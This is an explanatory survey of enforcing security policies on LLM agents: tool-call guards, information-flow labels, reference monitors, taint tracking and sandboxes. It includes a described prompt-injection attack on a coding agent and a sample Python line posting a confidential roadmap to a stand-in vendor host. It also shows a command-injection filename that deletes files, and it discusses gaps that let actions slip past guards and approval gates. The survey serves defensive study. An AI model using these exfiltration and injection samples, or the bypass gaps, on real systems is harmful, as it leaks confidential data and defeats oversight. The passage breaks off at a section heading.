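# Where to enforce an AI agent's security policy: libraries, interpreters, capability languages and sandboxes

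## What it takes to enforce a policy on an agent's actions

An AI agent is a language model that acts on a computer system for a user, for example by reading files, sending email, booking travel or running code. The model only produces text. The software around it, called the harness, passes it the user's request and a list of tools, carries out any action specified in the reply, adds the result to the conversation and queries the model again, until a reply contains no further actions. A security policy is a rule about which actions are allowed, for instance that a confidential document may not leave the company. Enforcing the policy requires a check between the model's text and the actions carried out from it, and where that check sits largely determines what it can stop.

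The requests come in three forms. A tool call is a structured request to run one named function with given arguments, such as `send_email` with a recipient and a body. An agent program is code written by the model, usually a few lines of Python, that combines several tool calls with its own logic. A shell command is a line of text for the operating system's command interpreter, and it is the hardest to judge in advance. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) points out that a command can load scripts and launch other programs, so one call to a shell tool may perform many file and network operations that its text does not reveal.

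### Why the check sits outside the model

A language model receives its instructions in the same stream as the text it reads, some of which strangers wrote. In a prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by hiding instructions in a web page, an email or a document, and the agent follows them. Kim and colleagues describe an attack in which every command looks like ordinary development work. A user asks an agent to compare a confidential project with related work on the web. One PDF the agent downloads contains an instruction to install a package named acme-compare. Installing the package overwrites a protected directory with the attacker's code. The agent then runs the package on the design document, which sends the document to the attacker's server.

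The usual benchmark for such attacks is AgentDojo. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) built it by combining 97 user tasks in four simulated environments (office workspace, Slack, travel booking and banking) with attackers' goals planted in the data that tools return. It had 629 security cases at first, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900. After each run, fixed code checks the state of the environment to decide whether the user's task and the attacker's task succeeded. The results give the attack success rate and the utility, which is the share of legitimate tasks that an agent completes under a defence.

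Training the model to refuse, or writing the policy into its prompt, puts the model in the trusted base, meaning all the code that must be correct for a guarantee to hold. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) argues that the guarantee is then only a probability. A model that correctly denies 99% of unauthorised requests still allows 1%, and an attacker can search for wording that gets through. Using a second model to judge the first has the same weakness. In *Ring-0 by Default*, Li, Huang and colleagues (2026) tested three command-line coding agents (Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI) and found a model-based permission monitor whose input included text that the agent controlled. Asking the user works little better in practice. Kim and colleagues cite Anthropic's figure that users approve roughly 93% of the permission prompts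 in Claude Code, and pay less attention as the number of prompts grows.

That leaves ordinary, deterministic code outside the model. Better-trained models still help, since they attempt fewer bad actions. They just can't carry the guarantee.

### One task, four programs

A small task makes the rest concrete. A user asks an agent to compare a vendor's offer with the company's internal roadmap and to email the result to the user. The offer comes from outside and may contain anything. The roadmap is confidential. A planner model, which has read the user's request and neither document, writes this program:

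```python
offer = read_file("inbox/vendor_offer.txt")     # untrusted
roadmap = read_file("internal/roadmap.md")      # confidential
question = "How does the offer fit the roadmap?"
summary = ask_model(question, offer, roadmap)
send_email(to=USER, body=summary)
```

`USER` is the user's address, which the harness supplies. `ask_model` passes text to a quarantined model, which reads untrusted data but has no tools, and returns the model's answer as a string. The program obeys the policy's two rules: information from the roadmap may reach only the user, and no outsider may choose where an email goes.

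Three variants break the policy in different ways. Program A takes the recipient's address from the offer:

```python
address = ask_model("Who should get the comparison?", offer)
send_email(to=address, body=summary)
```

The agent is allowed to use the tool and the arguments are well formed, but the vendor has chosen the recipient. A general ban on addresses found in documents would also block normal requests, such as "reply to the contact named in the offer".

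In program B the roadmap leaves by a direct HTTP request, and the email tool never runs:

```python
import urllib.request
urllib.request.urlopen("https://vendor.example/in",
                       data=roadmap.encode())
```

Program C sends no part of the roadmap anywhere. It posts one of two fixed sentences on a public page:

```python
if "acquisition" in roadmap:
    post_public("Our review will take another week.")
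else:
    post_public("Our review is on schedule.")
```

A vendor who knows the program learns from the post whether the roadmap mentions an acquisition. The post reveals only one bit, but a loop that tests the document bit by bit and posts each time would reveal all of it. Information that travels through the program's choice of branch, without any value being copied, is called an implicit flow.

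The check works the same way whether an attacker steered the model into writing A, B or C or the model wrote it by mistake.

### The reference monitor

The standard for such a check comes from *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report to the US Air Force on computers shared by people with different clearances. The report considers a "malicious user" who has legitimate access to the machine and can write arbitrary programs for it, much like an agent after a successful injection. It proposes a reference monitor, a component that checks every reference by any program to any other program, data or device against a list of what the user may do.

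Anderson set three requirements for an enforcement mechanism. It must be tamper-proof, because an attacker who can alter a check can bypass it. It must always run. If it is suspended for some programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must meet the same standard. It must also be small enough to analyze and test completely, which Anderson's second volume equates with being capable of proof. Otherwise, nobody can know whether it meets the first two requirements.

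The report gives an example of failure from the HIS 635 computer, where a hardware register confined each user's program to its own region of memory. But to read or write a device, the program had to call the operating system, GCOS III, which ran mostly with the memory check switched off, so the check did not always run. If GCOS III itself is counted as the monitor, the monitor has 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse. A Python harness can fail in the same two ways. A developer can put a check into `send_email`, but program B bypasses it. If the developer then treats the whole Python runtime as the monitor, nobody can verify it.

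Rules in a prompt do even worse. Li and colleagues judge that they meet none of the three requirements. Injected text can override the rules, nothing forces the model to consult them, and nobody can prove that the model will obey them.

Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, made complete mediation a design principle, meaning that the system must check every access to every object for authority. They also warned that a system that saves the result of a check for speed must update it when the authority changes. Agents face this problem whenever work waits in a queue. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) gives the example of a message that someone approved but that is still unsent when the approval is withdrawn or the contact changes.

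Deployed agents fail to achieve complete mediation in a simpler way. In Li and colleagues' experiments, individual tools did the access checks, so a file write that the file tool refused could still go through the shell. Similarly, the built-in web-fetching tool checked which host it was contacting but the shell did not, which is the same gap as in program B.

Saltzer and Schroeder's other relevant principle is least privilege: every program and user should have only the rights needed for the job. An agent's job is known only once the user has stated it. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an instruction to comment on a particular GitLab issue. The agent needs access to that issue and write access to its comment box, and nothing else in GitLab. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent no longer needs the comment box. A person or program has to derive such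 a policy from the request, and even complete enforcement doesn't correct a bad policy.

### Ambient authority and capabilities

Program B works because of ambient authority, which is power that any code in a process has without being explicitly granted it. In Python, any line can import a networking module or open a file by name. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a careful developer who gives an agent a small library for building bibliographies, with a function that appends entries fetched from the publication database DBLP. The agent may write arbitrary code around the library, so that code can skip the safe function and call the standard `writeFile` to save an entry that the model made up.

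The alternative is to require code to hold a capability, an unforgeable value that grants its holder the right to use a resource. Saltzer and Schroeder call it a "ticket". A web address, by contrast, is a string that anyone can type. If opening a connection took a capability, and the harness gave the agent's program one for the user's mailbox but none for the network, there would be no way to write a working version of program B. Object-capability languages build in this rule, whereas Python lets code use resources without holding a capability.

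Capabilities do nothing about program A, however. That program may send email, and it does. What is wrong is where the address came from.

### Labels for secrecy and trust

Information-flow control labels each piece of data to record who may read it or how far its source is trusted, and restricts where labelled data may go. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) traces the use of such labels back to Denning's work of 1976. The smallest useful scheme has two values for trust and two for secrecy. The trust values are T (trusted) and U (untrusted), with $T \sqsubseteq U$. The secrecy values are L (public, or low) and H (secret, or high), with $L \sqsubseteq H$. In both orders, the higher value carries more restrictions.

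When a program combines two pieces of data, the result gets the join of their labels, written $\sqcup$: the lowest label that is at least as restrictive as both. Take the summary in the benign program. The offer is untrusted and, for simplicity, public, so its label is $(U, L)$. The roadmap is trusted and secret, $(T, H)$. Then

$$(U, L) \sqcup (T, H) = (U \sqcup T,\; L \sqcup H) = (U, H).$$

The summary is untrusted because a stranger's text shaped it, and secret because it may repeat the roadmap. A lattice is an ordered set in which any two labels have a join like this one and a greatest label below both. Two levels each for trust and secrecy are often too coarse, so Kim and colleagues also use sets of permitted readers as labels. The join of two such sets is their intersection, so if Ann, Bo and Cy may read one document and Bo, Cy and Di may read another, only Bo and Cy may read a text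 based on both.

The idea predates AI agents by decades. Saltzer and Schroeder mention ADEPT, an early system that tracked the classification of every input to a file and marked all output with the highest one.

Kim and colleagues state two policies over these labels. The integrity policy permits an action only if the decision to take it, and every argument that matters, rests on trusted data. The confidentiality policy permits data to leave only if all recipients may read it. The benign program passes both because its plan came from the user's request alone, the recipient is a trusted constant, and the user may read the roadmap. Program A fails the integrity policy because `address` comes from the offer and has trust label U. It fails even when the address belongs to a colleague who may read the roadmap, which the confidentiality policy alone would allow.

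Labels that follow only copied and computed values miss the problem in program C. Both of its sentences are constants in a program that a trusted planner wrote, so their labels are $(T, L)$ and the post looks harmless. For this reason, *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), which introduced an agent planner named FIDES, claims only that tracking labels as the program runs can enforce *explicit* secrecy and integrity. To stop program C, a mechanism must also track the label of the condition that chose the branch.

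### What a monitor of one run can enforce

Program C is hard for a deeper reason. In *Enforceable Security Policies*, Schneider (2000) asked which policies can be enforced by a mechanism that only watches the steps of a running program and halts it before a violation. Reference monitors, firewalls and most operating-system checks work this way.

Schneider defines a policy very broadly, as any condition $P$ on the set $\Pi$ of all runs that a program could produce. A monitor has only the present run to go on. It can therefore enforce $P$ only if $P$ reduces to a test $\hat{P}$ that each run passes or fails by itself:

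$$P(\Pi) \iff \forall \sigma \in \Pi : \hat{P}(\sigma).$$

The monitor cannot observe future steps, which adds two more conditions. If a partial run fails the test, every continuation of it must fail too, because the program might stop at that point. And every run that fails must do so after finitely many steps, or the monitor could never intervene. Policies that meet all three conditions are safety properties, which require that some definite bad thing never happens. For example, "No email to an address outside this list" is a safety property, but "The user eventually gets an answer" is not, since any unfinished run might still produce the answer.

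Secrecy fails the first condition. Suppose that program C posts that the review is on schedule. Nothing in that run is objectionable. The post leaks information because a different roadmap would have produced a different post, but the monitor never observes that other run. The user wants noninterference, which means that changing the protected input must not change what an outsider observes. This property compares runs, so no test on single runs expresses it exactly.

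A monitor can still enforce a stricter policy. Schneider's example is a rule that forbids sending after a file read. The monitor starts in a state where everything is allowed, moves to a second state at the first file read, and halts the program if it then tries to send. In the running example, this rule stops A, B and C, but it also stops the benign program, which reads two files and then sends an email. A run-time check that guards secrecy has to forbid some harmless runs, and the number it forbids is what matters in practice.

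The rule also depends on a correct list of what counts as sending. Schneider warns that some ways to send may be "buried deep within the bowels of the target", and the list must include all of them. If it holds only `send_email` and `post_public`, program B gets through, and the theorem does not prevent this.

Two kinds of mechanism fall outside Schneider's class. A compiler or theorem prover examines the program's text before it runs and can reason about every branch, including those a given run does not take. A monitor that can hold back effects and release them later can also enforce more policies than one that can only halt the program. *Kairos* (2026), a design that stages an agent's effects at the edge of its isolation layer, relies on this ability. In Schneider's example, a shop must deliver once a customer has paid, and a monitor that can only halt the program cannot guarantee the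 delivery. A monitor that holds the payment until the delivery is ready could release the two together. But it would still judge one run at a time, so the added ability does not settle program C.

### Four places for the check, and three measures

The check can sit in any of four places:

- A library in the host language, the general-purpose language (usually Python) in which the harness runs. The library may consist of guards, which are wrappers or hooks that run before an action, or of data types that carry labels. It has the tool's name and arguments at hand, and nothing obliges the agent's code to go through it.
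- An interpreter built for the agent's programs, which executes them statement by statement and offers no operation that the designer left out. Anderson already thought that a programmed interpreter might serve as the monitor for a query system whose users could do no general programming. For general use the report called for hardware, on grounds of efficiency.
- A language whose compiler rejects unsafe programs before they start.
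- The operating system beneath, where a sandbox or a kernel-level monitor intercepts file and network operations whatever code issued them.

Enforcing a policy at this low a level makes it harder to bypass, but the checks become less precise. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) ranks ways of making sure that every effect passes the check, from a convention that all calls go through one point in the agent framework up to interception in the kernel or the network layer. Interception at those layers doesn't depend on the programmer's discipline, but it takes more work to integrate. Schneider objects that operating-system concepts are a coarse vocabulary for policy. A kernel handles connections and bytes, which are often encrypted, and has no representation of a roadmap or a recipient.

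Completeness measures what gets past a mechanism. It covers which of programs A, B and C the mechanism stops while still letting the benign program run, and how much code belongs to the trusted base. The hardest version is a worst-case injection test, which assumes that the attacker controls the model's output once the model has read the injected text. Developer effort includes wrapping or annotating tools, writing labels and policies, and learning any new language. Runtime overhead is the added time and model calls, including retries after a refusal. It depends heavily on how often the check has to act. Schneider observed that a monitor that must step in at every machine instruction could add a great deal of overhead, while one that acts only on system calls, where the program already hands control to the operating system, can add little.

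## Guards wrapped around tool calls

Developers most often put the check in the harness itself. Every harness has a function that reads the tool name and arguments from the model's reply and calls the tool, and a developer can add a guard there with a few lines of code. *Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) argues that this is the natural place because all of an agent's effects on the outside world pass through tool calls. It adds that ordinary code can test a tool call's name and typed arguments, unlike the free text in which the model reasons. The point about typed arguments is hard to dispute, but whether every effect passes through a guarded call depends on what the tools can do.

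### Exposing a tool is not authorising a call

*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examined the public source code of two popular agent frameworks, LangChain/LangGraph and LlamaIndex, and of Stripe's toolkit for agents that handle payments. All three let the developer choose which tools an agent has, but none checks by default whether a particular call, with particular values, is allowed. LangChain looks up the tool by name, usually checks that the arguments have the right shape, and runs it. The Stripe toolkit adds a list of permitted actions and relies on the limits of the merchant's API key. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount, currency and customer the model supplied.

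A type check accepts `acct_ATTACKER_999` as an account because it is a well-formed string. Mellafe Zuvic calls this a confused deputy problem, using Norm Hardy's 1988 term for a program that someone else tricks into misusing its legitimate authority. In a test on a mock payment system, he gave LangChain a fixed model output containing a call to move a merchant's payouts to that account, and LangChain made the change. His own guard, ScopeGate, blocked the same call because the account was not in the operator's verified set.

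ScopeGate checks that the policy lists the tool, that restricted arguments have permitted values, that any sum of money is under a ceiling, and that calls that must not be repeated carry an identifying key. It refuses everything else, including any call that makes the guard crash. The program is small but still easy to get wrong. An early version let through a payment whose amount was NaN, the floating-point value for "not a number", because every greater-than comparison with NaN is false. The corrected version blocked all 48 hand-written attempts to bypass it. It also blocked all 29 unauthorised calls that an attacking model made over 40 rounds, with the reason for each refusal given to the model. This second result is encouraging, but it comes from only one attacker with a small budget.

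Mellafe Zuvic requires that no part of the design's policy come from a model's output, even indirectly. Otherwise, an injection that corrupts a call could also corrupt the rule for judging that call.

### Rules about a single call

Progent relaxes that condition. Its policies are lists of rules that allow or forbid a tool call when the arguments meet some test. Forbid rules take precedence, and a call that matches no rule fails. In the running example, one rule would allow `send_email` only when `to` equals the user's address. Writing such rules by hand for every request would be impractical, so a language model drafts them from the user's request before the agent reads anything untrusted.

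The difficulty is that agents learn what they need as they go. If the user says "do what Alice's email asks", the necessary tools become clear only once the agent has read the email, which may also contain an injection. Progent lets the model propose a new policy after each step and passes it to an SMT solver, a program that decides questions about logical formulas. If $A(P)$ is the set of calls that policy $P$ allows, a new policy $P'$ takes effect automatically only when

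$$A(P') \subseteq A(P).$$

Any other change needs approval from a person or a predefined rule, so a manipulated model cannot silently widen the agent's permissions.

Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo with GPT-4o from 39.9% to 1.0%. But Shi and colleagues set the approver to accept every expansion, to imitate a careless user, so the solver's comparison blocked nothing in that test. The gain came from the policies the model wrote, and the first draft alone brought the rate down to 2.5%. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that updates may loosen the rules when tool results contain injected text. The solver prevents this only if the approver rejects the bad expansions. It also doesn't help when a policy is too broad from the start. In Progent's own example, the agent is allowed to send Slack messages to anyone for one step,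 until it has looked up the user's handle.

*AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) takes the opposite default and lets an action go ahead unless a rule intervenes. Each rule has a trigger, a condition and a response. For example, a rule can require the agent to ask the user before a bank transfer if the recipient is not a verified family member. Rules can also stop the run, substitute another action or have the model reconsider. AgentSpec hooks into LangChain's loop before each action, after each result and at the end of the task.

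When the agent writes code, AgentSpec's rules trigger when the Python interpreter starts, and their conditions search the program's text for things such as a web address outside an approved list. In tests on 25 categories of risky code, the rules intercepted over 90% of the unsafe programs. But Wang and colleagues wrote those rules from descriptions of the same risks, and they acknowledge that analysing data flow would make detection more accurate. A text search will miss an address that the program assembles from fragments as it runs.

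### FORGE: rules about what came before

Whether an email leaks data can depend on whether the agent has already read a confidential document, so a guard that checks only the call cannot distinguish a leak from a harmless email with the same text. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, a guard that records which earlier events may have influenced each call.

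FORGE starts by wrapping the function that dispatches tool calls in each supported framework, including LangChain and Google's Agent Development Kit. The wrapper pauses each call, gets a verdict, and continues only if the verdict allows it. FORGE also wraps the functions that send requests in `httpx` and `requests`, two widely used Python HTTP libraries, so that a tool that contacts a server directly goes through the same check.

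The wrappers also build an event graph. Its nodes are messages, tool calls and tool results, and an edge runs from each event to any later event it may have influenced. A model's reply, for example, has an edge from every message in the model's context, whether or not the model used it. The graph includes edges that may be unnecessary because a missing edge can hide a leak, while an extra one can at worst cause a needless refusal.

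When a tool call arrives, FORGE finds the message that initiated it and waits until the policy engine has received that message's whole history. It then writes the call, the user's identity and the history as facts in Datalog, a logic language whose programs derive new facts from given ones until no more can be derived. On a finite set of facts, a Datalog program always finishes.

The vendor task is close to Palumbo and colleagues' own example. Suppose that the agent makes its calls one at a time, reading the offer and the roadmap and then sending the email. FORGE records the offer as untrusted input, the roadmap as sensitive input, and the email as dependent on both. The policy, with `:-` meaning "if" and a comma meaning "and", is:

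```prolog
Tainted(x)   :- UntrustedInput(x).
Tainted(x)   :- DependsOn(x, y), Tainted(y).
HasSecret(x) :- SensitiveInput(x).
HasSecret(x) :- DependsOn(x, y), HasSecret(y).
Deny(x)      :- ExternalSend(x), Tainted(x), HasSecret(x).
```

The model's reply is tainted because it depends on the offer, and the email is tainted because it depends on the reply. By the same steps, the email counts as carrying a secret. If the email goes to the user, `ExternalSend` does not hold and FORGE releases it. If it goes to an outside address, all three conditions hold, so FORGE blocks the call and returns an explanation to the agent. A derived `Deny` always overrides a derived `Allow`, and if neither is derived, the deployment's default applies.

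With a history of the agent's actions, a policy can also require one action before allowing another. In VS Code's Copilot Chat, a FORGE policy blocked `git push` until a security scan had covered every recent edit. A scan that ran before the edits did not count, because the graph had no path from the edits to the scan.

Palumbo and colleagues guarantee that a forbidden action never runs, provided that every relevant action reaches the monitor before it takes effect and the facts describe events faithfully. The second condition is less certain to hold when a policy calls a language model. In one case study, a model checked whether replies revealed why someone was unavailable, and Palumbo and colleagues call that form of enforcement probabilistic.

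The AgentDojo test of FORGE used GPT-4o and one type of attack, with 949 attacked runs, each repeated five times. Attacks succeeded 14.1% of the time against the baseline agent, which had the user's request repeated to it after each batch of tool results. Adding the FIDES policy, which forbids consequential actions once the context contains untrusted text, lowered the rate to 0.6%. Adding instead a policy that checks each argument, and accepts a destination only if it came from the user's request, the operator's records or another trusted source, lowered it to 0.9%. Some of the remaining successes were calls that FORGE had blocked but the benchmark still counted. Without them, the rates are 0.3% and 0.2%, and the successes that remain involve the agent's final text answer, which no guard checked. Both policies also reduced the share of legitimate tasks completed when no attack was under way,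 from 83.7% for the baseline agent to 62.5% with the argument policy and 33.2% with the FIDES policy.

### Where an argument came from, and how often

A rule that applies to individual arguments blocks fewer legitimate tasks than one that applies to the whole context. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) takes this approach further. In its example, an agent is allowed to send Alice the public fields of a private report, but only once. The policy requires the message body to come from a function that selects the approved fields, the address to come from a designated directory lookup, and the number of attempts to stay within a quota.

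The agent passes a handle to a stored value, never the text itself, and the guard fetches the value and its history. The agent therefore cannot submit the raw report and claim it is the summary, and identical text from another source fails the check. The guard deducts each attempt from the quota before it calls the mail tool, so a failed delivery still counts against the quota.

When permissions have quotas, widening one can block a workflow that the policy used to allow. For example, suppose an agent may delete B once and A once, and the guard searches the permissions in that order. A developer then widens the first permission to cover either object. If the agent deletes A first, it uses up the widened permission and can no longer delete B, but it can delete A again, which the old policy forbade. Shivakumar and colleagues wrote checks that certify a revision only if it preserves every workflow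 that the old policy allowed. On 51 test revisions, the checks certified all 21 that did so and none of the other 30.

The part of Agenra that decides whether to allow each call is written in Lean, a language in which programs can include machine-checked proofs. The proofs do not cover the Python code that translates policies and dispatches calls, which therefore remains in the trusted base.

### The test programs against a guard

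Even a simple guard stops Program A, which takes the recipient's address from the offer, if the policy names the user as the only allowed recipient. The guard needs provenance when the user says "reply to the contact named in the offer", because no list can contain that address in advance. FORGE's tainted-and-secret rule stops A when the address is external, but allows the email if the vendor names a colleague, even though the vendor has still chosen the recipient. A rule like Agenra's, which ties the recipient to one designated source, blocks that email too.

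However, A is a program that the planner model wrote before reading either file. The program passes the texts through Python variables, which the wrappers do not record. If the guard links the email only to the message that contained the program, it finds no path back to the offer or the roadmap and allows the email to be sent. The developer has to add the missing edges, for instance by treating every call in a program as dependent on all results the program has received so far.

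With those edges, the guard also stops program C, which reveals one bit of the roadmap by choosing between two fixed sentences. The guard blocks the public post because it is an external send that follows both an untrusted and a secret input. The same rule blocks every later public post in that program, even harmless ones. If the program had not read the offer, the rule would have permitted the leak, because it blocks an external send only after both kinds of input.

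Program B sends the roadmap by a direct HTTP request. FORGE as published does not stop the request because the program uses `urllib`, from Python's standard library, and FORGE wraps only `httpx` and `requests`. A developer can wrap `urllib` too, but Palumbo and colleagues state that FORGE still cannot control code that writes to a raw network socket.

### Actions that run while approval is pending

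A rule that ends in "ask the user" relies on the framework to hold the action until the user decides. Frameworks offer approval gates for this, and also ways to cancel a run or limit its duration. In *Stop Means Stop* (July 2026), Sajjad Khan tested these controls in six open-source frameworks: LangGraph, its JavaScript port LangGraph.js, LlamaIndex Workflows, Microsoft Agent Framework, the OpenAI Agents SDK and CrewAI.

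Each test program, or probe, is the smallest workflow that exercises one control. It is built from ordinary functions, with no language model, and each action adds a line to a log. Khan decided before each run what would count as a violation, so each probe has a yes-or-no result for the framework. For approval gates, a violation was an action that took effect while the run was paused.

In all five frameworks that place an approval gate before an action, the gate failed to stop other actions in the same step. (CrewAI offers human review only after a tool has run, so it had no such gate to test.) The frameworks run independent branches of a step in parallel, and the gate suspends only its own branch. Suppose an agent requests approval to email a customer and, in the same step, issues the customer a refund. The refund goes out while the user is still reading the request, so a rejection comes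 too late to stop it. Khan calls this a sibling leak. In 1,000 randomly generated LangGraph workflows, all 577 actions that shared a step with the gate but did not depend on it ran during the pause. None of the 694 actions that came later or depended on the gate did.

The probes also found that LangGraph, in both languages, restarts a step after approval and so repeats any action the step had already taken. LlamaIndex, Microsoft's framework and the OpenAI SDK keep completed work instead of repeating it, which shows that the fault is avoidable. In all five Python frameworks, a cancelled tool running on a separate thread could still take effect after the caller had received notice of the cancellation.

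Khan measured the leak with live models by connecting four of them to LangGraph and running each 300 times across three tasks likely to produce parallel calls. The consequential action took effect during the pause in 215 of the 1,200 runs: 133 with GPT-4o, 56 with Llama 3.3 70B, 26 with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and none with DeepSeek. The leak occurred every time a model issued the parallel calls, as expected, because the test workflow put the pause on one branch and the action on another. The experiment's contribution is to measure how often models issue such calls, which depends heavily on the task.

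On τ-bench, a customer-service benchmark that Khan did not write, two models mostly looked things up in parallel and then acted one step at a time. None of the 71 batches that contained a consequential call also contained a harmless lookup, although GPT-4o sometimes issued two consequential calls together. On five jobs that needed two actions, such as deploying software and notifying the team, GPT-4o issued both at once in all 500 runs. An attacker can also cause a model to mix consequential calls with lookups. When a support ticket contained an injected demand for a refund, GPT-4o issued the refund alongside ordinary lookups in 95 of 100 runs, and each time the refund went through during the approval pause. Newer models may behave differently, but the fault is in how the frameworks schedule work.

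Khan's repair, SoundGate, is a separate program. Every tool must submit an action to it before performing that action. Each submission identifies the run and includes a key that stays the same if the action is repeated, and a flag for actions that need approval. SoundGate refuses the action if someone has cancelled the run, if it has already released an action with that key in the same run, or if the user has rejected it. If the action needs approval, SoundGate holds it until the user decides, and otherwise releases it. SoundGate keeps its record of cancellations, releases and user decisions outside the framework, so the same decision applies to a parallel branch, a restarted step and a leftover thread. With SoundGate in place, none of the 1,200 live runs leaked. Khan also verified a formal model of the decision logic and found no difference between the model and the running code over 12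 million operations.

A framework could instead make all parallel actions wait for the gate, or build an equivalent of SoundGate into its own code. Khan prefers an external gate because each framework's developers would have to make the change and preserve it in every later version, whereas whoever deploys an agent can add one gate on their own.

### Mediation by convention and by structure

SoundGate controls only the actions that tools submit to it, and *Stop Means Stop* distinguishes two ways to ensure that tools submit every action. One is mediation by convention, in which the developer must wrap every tool. If the developer forgets one, the guard fails open, so the action goes ahead and nobody notices. Scanning the code for direct calls catches some omissions, but it misses calls constructed at run time and calls inside third-party libraries.

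Under mediation by structure, the operating system's kernel blocks every network connection from the tool's process except the one to the gate. An unwrapped tool therefore gets a network error the first time it tries to act, and the developer finds a broken tool instead of a leak. Khan ran all five Python frameworks under such a restriction, and SoundGate worked in each without changes. Network rules do not cover files or memory shared with other processes, which need their own restrictions.

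FORGE's wrappers mediate tool calls only by convention, so whether they stop program B depends on which library it imports. A kernel rule stops B whichever library it uses. Agent code written in Python can also undo a wrapper in its own process by restoring the original function. Shivakumar and colleagues concede a similar point about Agenra, whose protection relies on Python object identity and does not isolate arbitrary Python code. The kernel rule does not stop program A, because A sends its email through a legitimate tool that submits it properly.

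### What a guard does well

A guard receives the details people use to state policies, such as a recipient, an amount or a reservation number, and it can look up the customer's record before deciding. Guards leave the agent and its tools unchanged, and Progent can run as a proxy between them. Using a guard doesn't require learning a new programming language, though FORGE and Agenra do require a policy language. The checks are also fast, and FORGE typically decides in under a millisecond.

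Guards can also help with ordinary mistakes. In *Reason Less, Verify More*, Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026) studied an airline customer-service agent in the benchmark τ²-bench. The agent's tools will cancel any existing reservation, even if the airline's written policy forbids it. In 78% of the agent's failures, the database ended up wrong and no tool had reported an error. They added four short Python guards that check the proposed call against the current database. With the guards, GPT-4o-mini completed 42.0% of tasks, up from 29.6%, and a repeat with three times as many runs found nearly the same gain.

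Almost all of it came from one guard, which checks whether a reservation is eligible for cancellation and was right all 161 times it intervened. Another was right in only 5% of its interventions, so each guard needs its own audit. Reddy and colleagues also let a call proceed if a guard crashes. That is reasonable for catching a model's mistakes but dangerous against an attacker who can find an input that crashes the guard.

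Guards work best when an agent has only narrow tools and cannot run code. Apart from the text of its answers, the agent can then act only through the dispatch function, so a guard there comes close to complete mediation. If one of the tools is a shell or a Python interpreter, the guard receives a single call whose argument is a whole program, with no separate recipient or amount to inspect.

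## Labelling data from inside an ordinary language

If a guard treats every call in an agent program as dependent on everything the program has read, it can't distinguish a call that uses the roadmap from one that doesn't. Labelling the value itself would let it do so. Web programmers used such labels, a technique called taint tracking, long before AI agents existed, because web applications insert text from strangers into database queries and shell commands.

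### Strings that carry a label

Perl, and later Ruby, built taint tracking into the interpreter. In 2010 Conti and Russo, in *A Taint Mode for Python via a Library*, showed that about 300 lines of ordinary Python can do the job, because Python lets a programmer define a subclass of a built-in type and override its methods. A much simplified labelled string looks like this:

```python
class TaintedStr(str):
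    tags = frozenset()

    def __add__(self, other):
        result = TaintedStr(str.__add__(self, other))
        result.tags = self.tags | getattr(other, "tags", frozenset())
        return result
```

Python calls `__add__` to evaluate `+`, so adding another string to a labelled one gives a labelled result with the tags of both. The union of the two tag sets serves as the join $\sqcup$. A labelled string is still a `str`, so existing code accepts it. Conti and Russo's library generates labelled classes automatically from a built-in type and a list of its methods. It wraps each method so that the result carries the tags of the object and of every argument.

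The example is a web application that mails users their stored files. It builds a shell command from an email address and a file name, so a visitor who enters `/etc/passwd ; rm -rf /` as the file name receives the server's account list and wipes the server's files. The developer marks both inputs as tainted and the shell call as a sensitive sink, an operation that tainted data must not reach. The library raises an alarm when the command reaches the shell. To let legitimate requests through, the developer registers a cleaning function that removes the taint tag from any text it processes. The lines that build and run the command do not change.

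In the vendor task, a developer would mark `read_file` as a source and have `send_email` reject a tagged `to` address. This alone would not stop program A, which takes the recipient from the offer. It gets the address from `ask_model`, which sends the offer to a model over the network and returns a new string with no tags. The developer has to wrap `ask_model` so that the answer inherits the tags of everything in the question, and the library has a helper for this. The check then stops A and lets the benign program run.

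### Where the label gets lost

A label survives only operations that a programmer has overridden to preserve it. *DjangoChecker* (Steinhauser and Tůma, 2019) extends the technique to search for flaws in Django web applications and describes several places where a naive version loses labels. If the left operand of `+` is a plain string, Python uses that string's method and returns a plain result, unless the labelled class defines `__radd__`, which lets the right operand handle the operation. Real applications also convert strings to lists of integers and back, so integers need labels too, and the functions `ord` and `chr`, which convert between characters and their codes, must preserve them.

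Labelling the contents of containers matters most. Splitting a string returns a list, and a Django database query often returns tuples, so the wrapper must label each element. On eight mature applications, DjangoChecker found 85 places where the application failed to clean text properly for the page it appeared on. It still found all 85 when Steinhauser and Tůma turned off labels on numbers, but only 13 when they also turned off labels in containers.

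Some gaps have no clean fix. Python does not allow subclasses of `bool`, so a true-or-false value can't carry a tag. Conti and Russo's library does not override `__repr__`, which produces an object's printable form, because doing so caused infinite recursion. Calling `repr` on a labelled string therefore returns an unlabelled copy. External libraries, especially those written in other languages, also return unlabelled values unless the developer wraps them too. Python has since added f-strings such as `f"Dear {name}"`, which language models often write. The interpreter assembles these internally and returns a plain `str`, whatever the class of `name`. Labels can also be lost when data is stored, so *Towards a Taint Mode for Cloud Computing Web Applications* (Bello and Russo, 2012) presents a follow-up library that covers Google App Engine's datastore.

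Program B, the direct HTTP request, goes through two of these gaps. It calls `roadmap.encode()`, which turns the text into bytes, and the published library has no labelled class for bytes. It then passes the bytes to `urlopen`, which nobody has declared a sink. Both failures are silent because an unlabelled value looks like harmless data.

Conti and Russo assume that the code under analysis is not malicious. Malicious code wouldn't have to exploit any of these gaps, because the tags are an ordinary Python attribute and a single line can empty the set.

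### Changing the runtime instead

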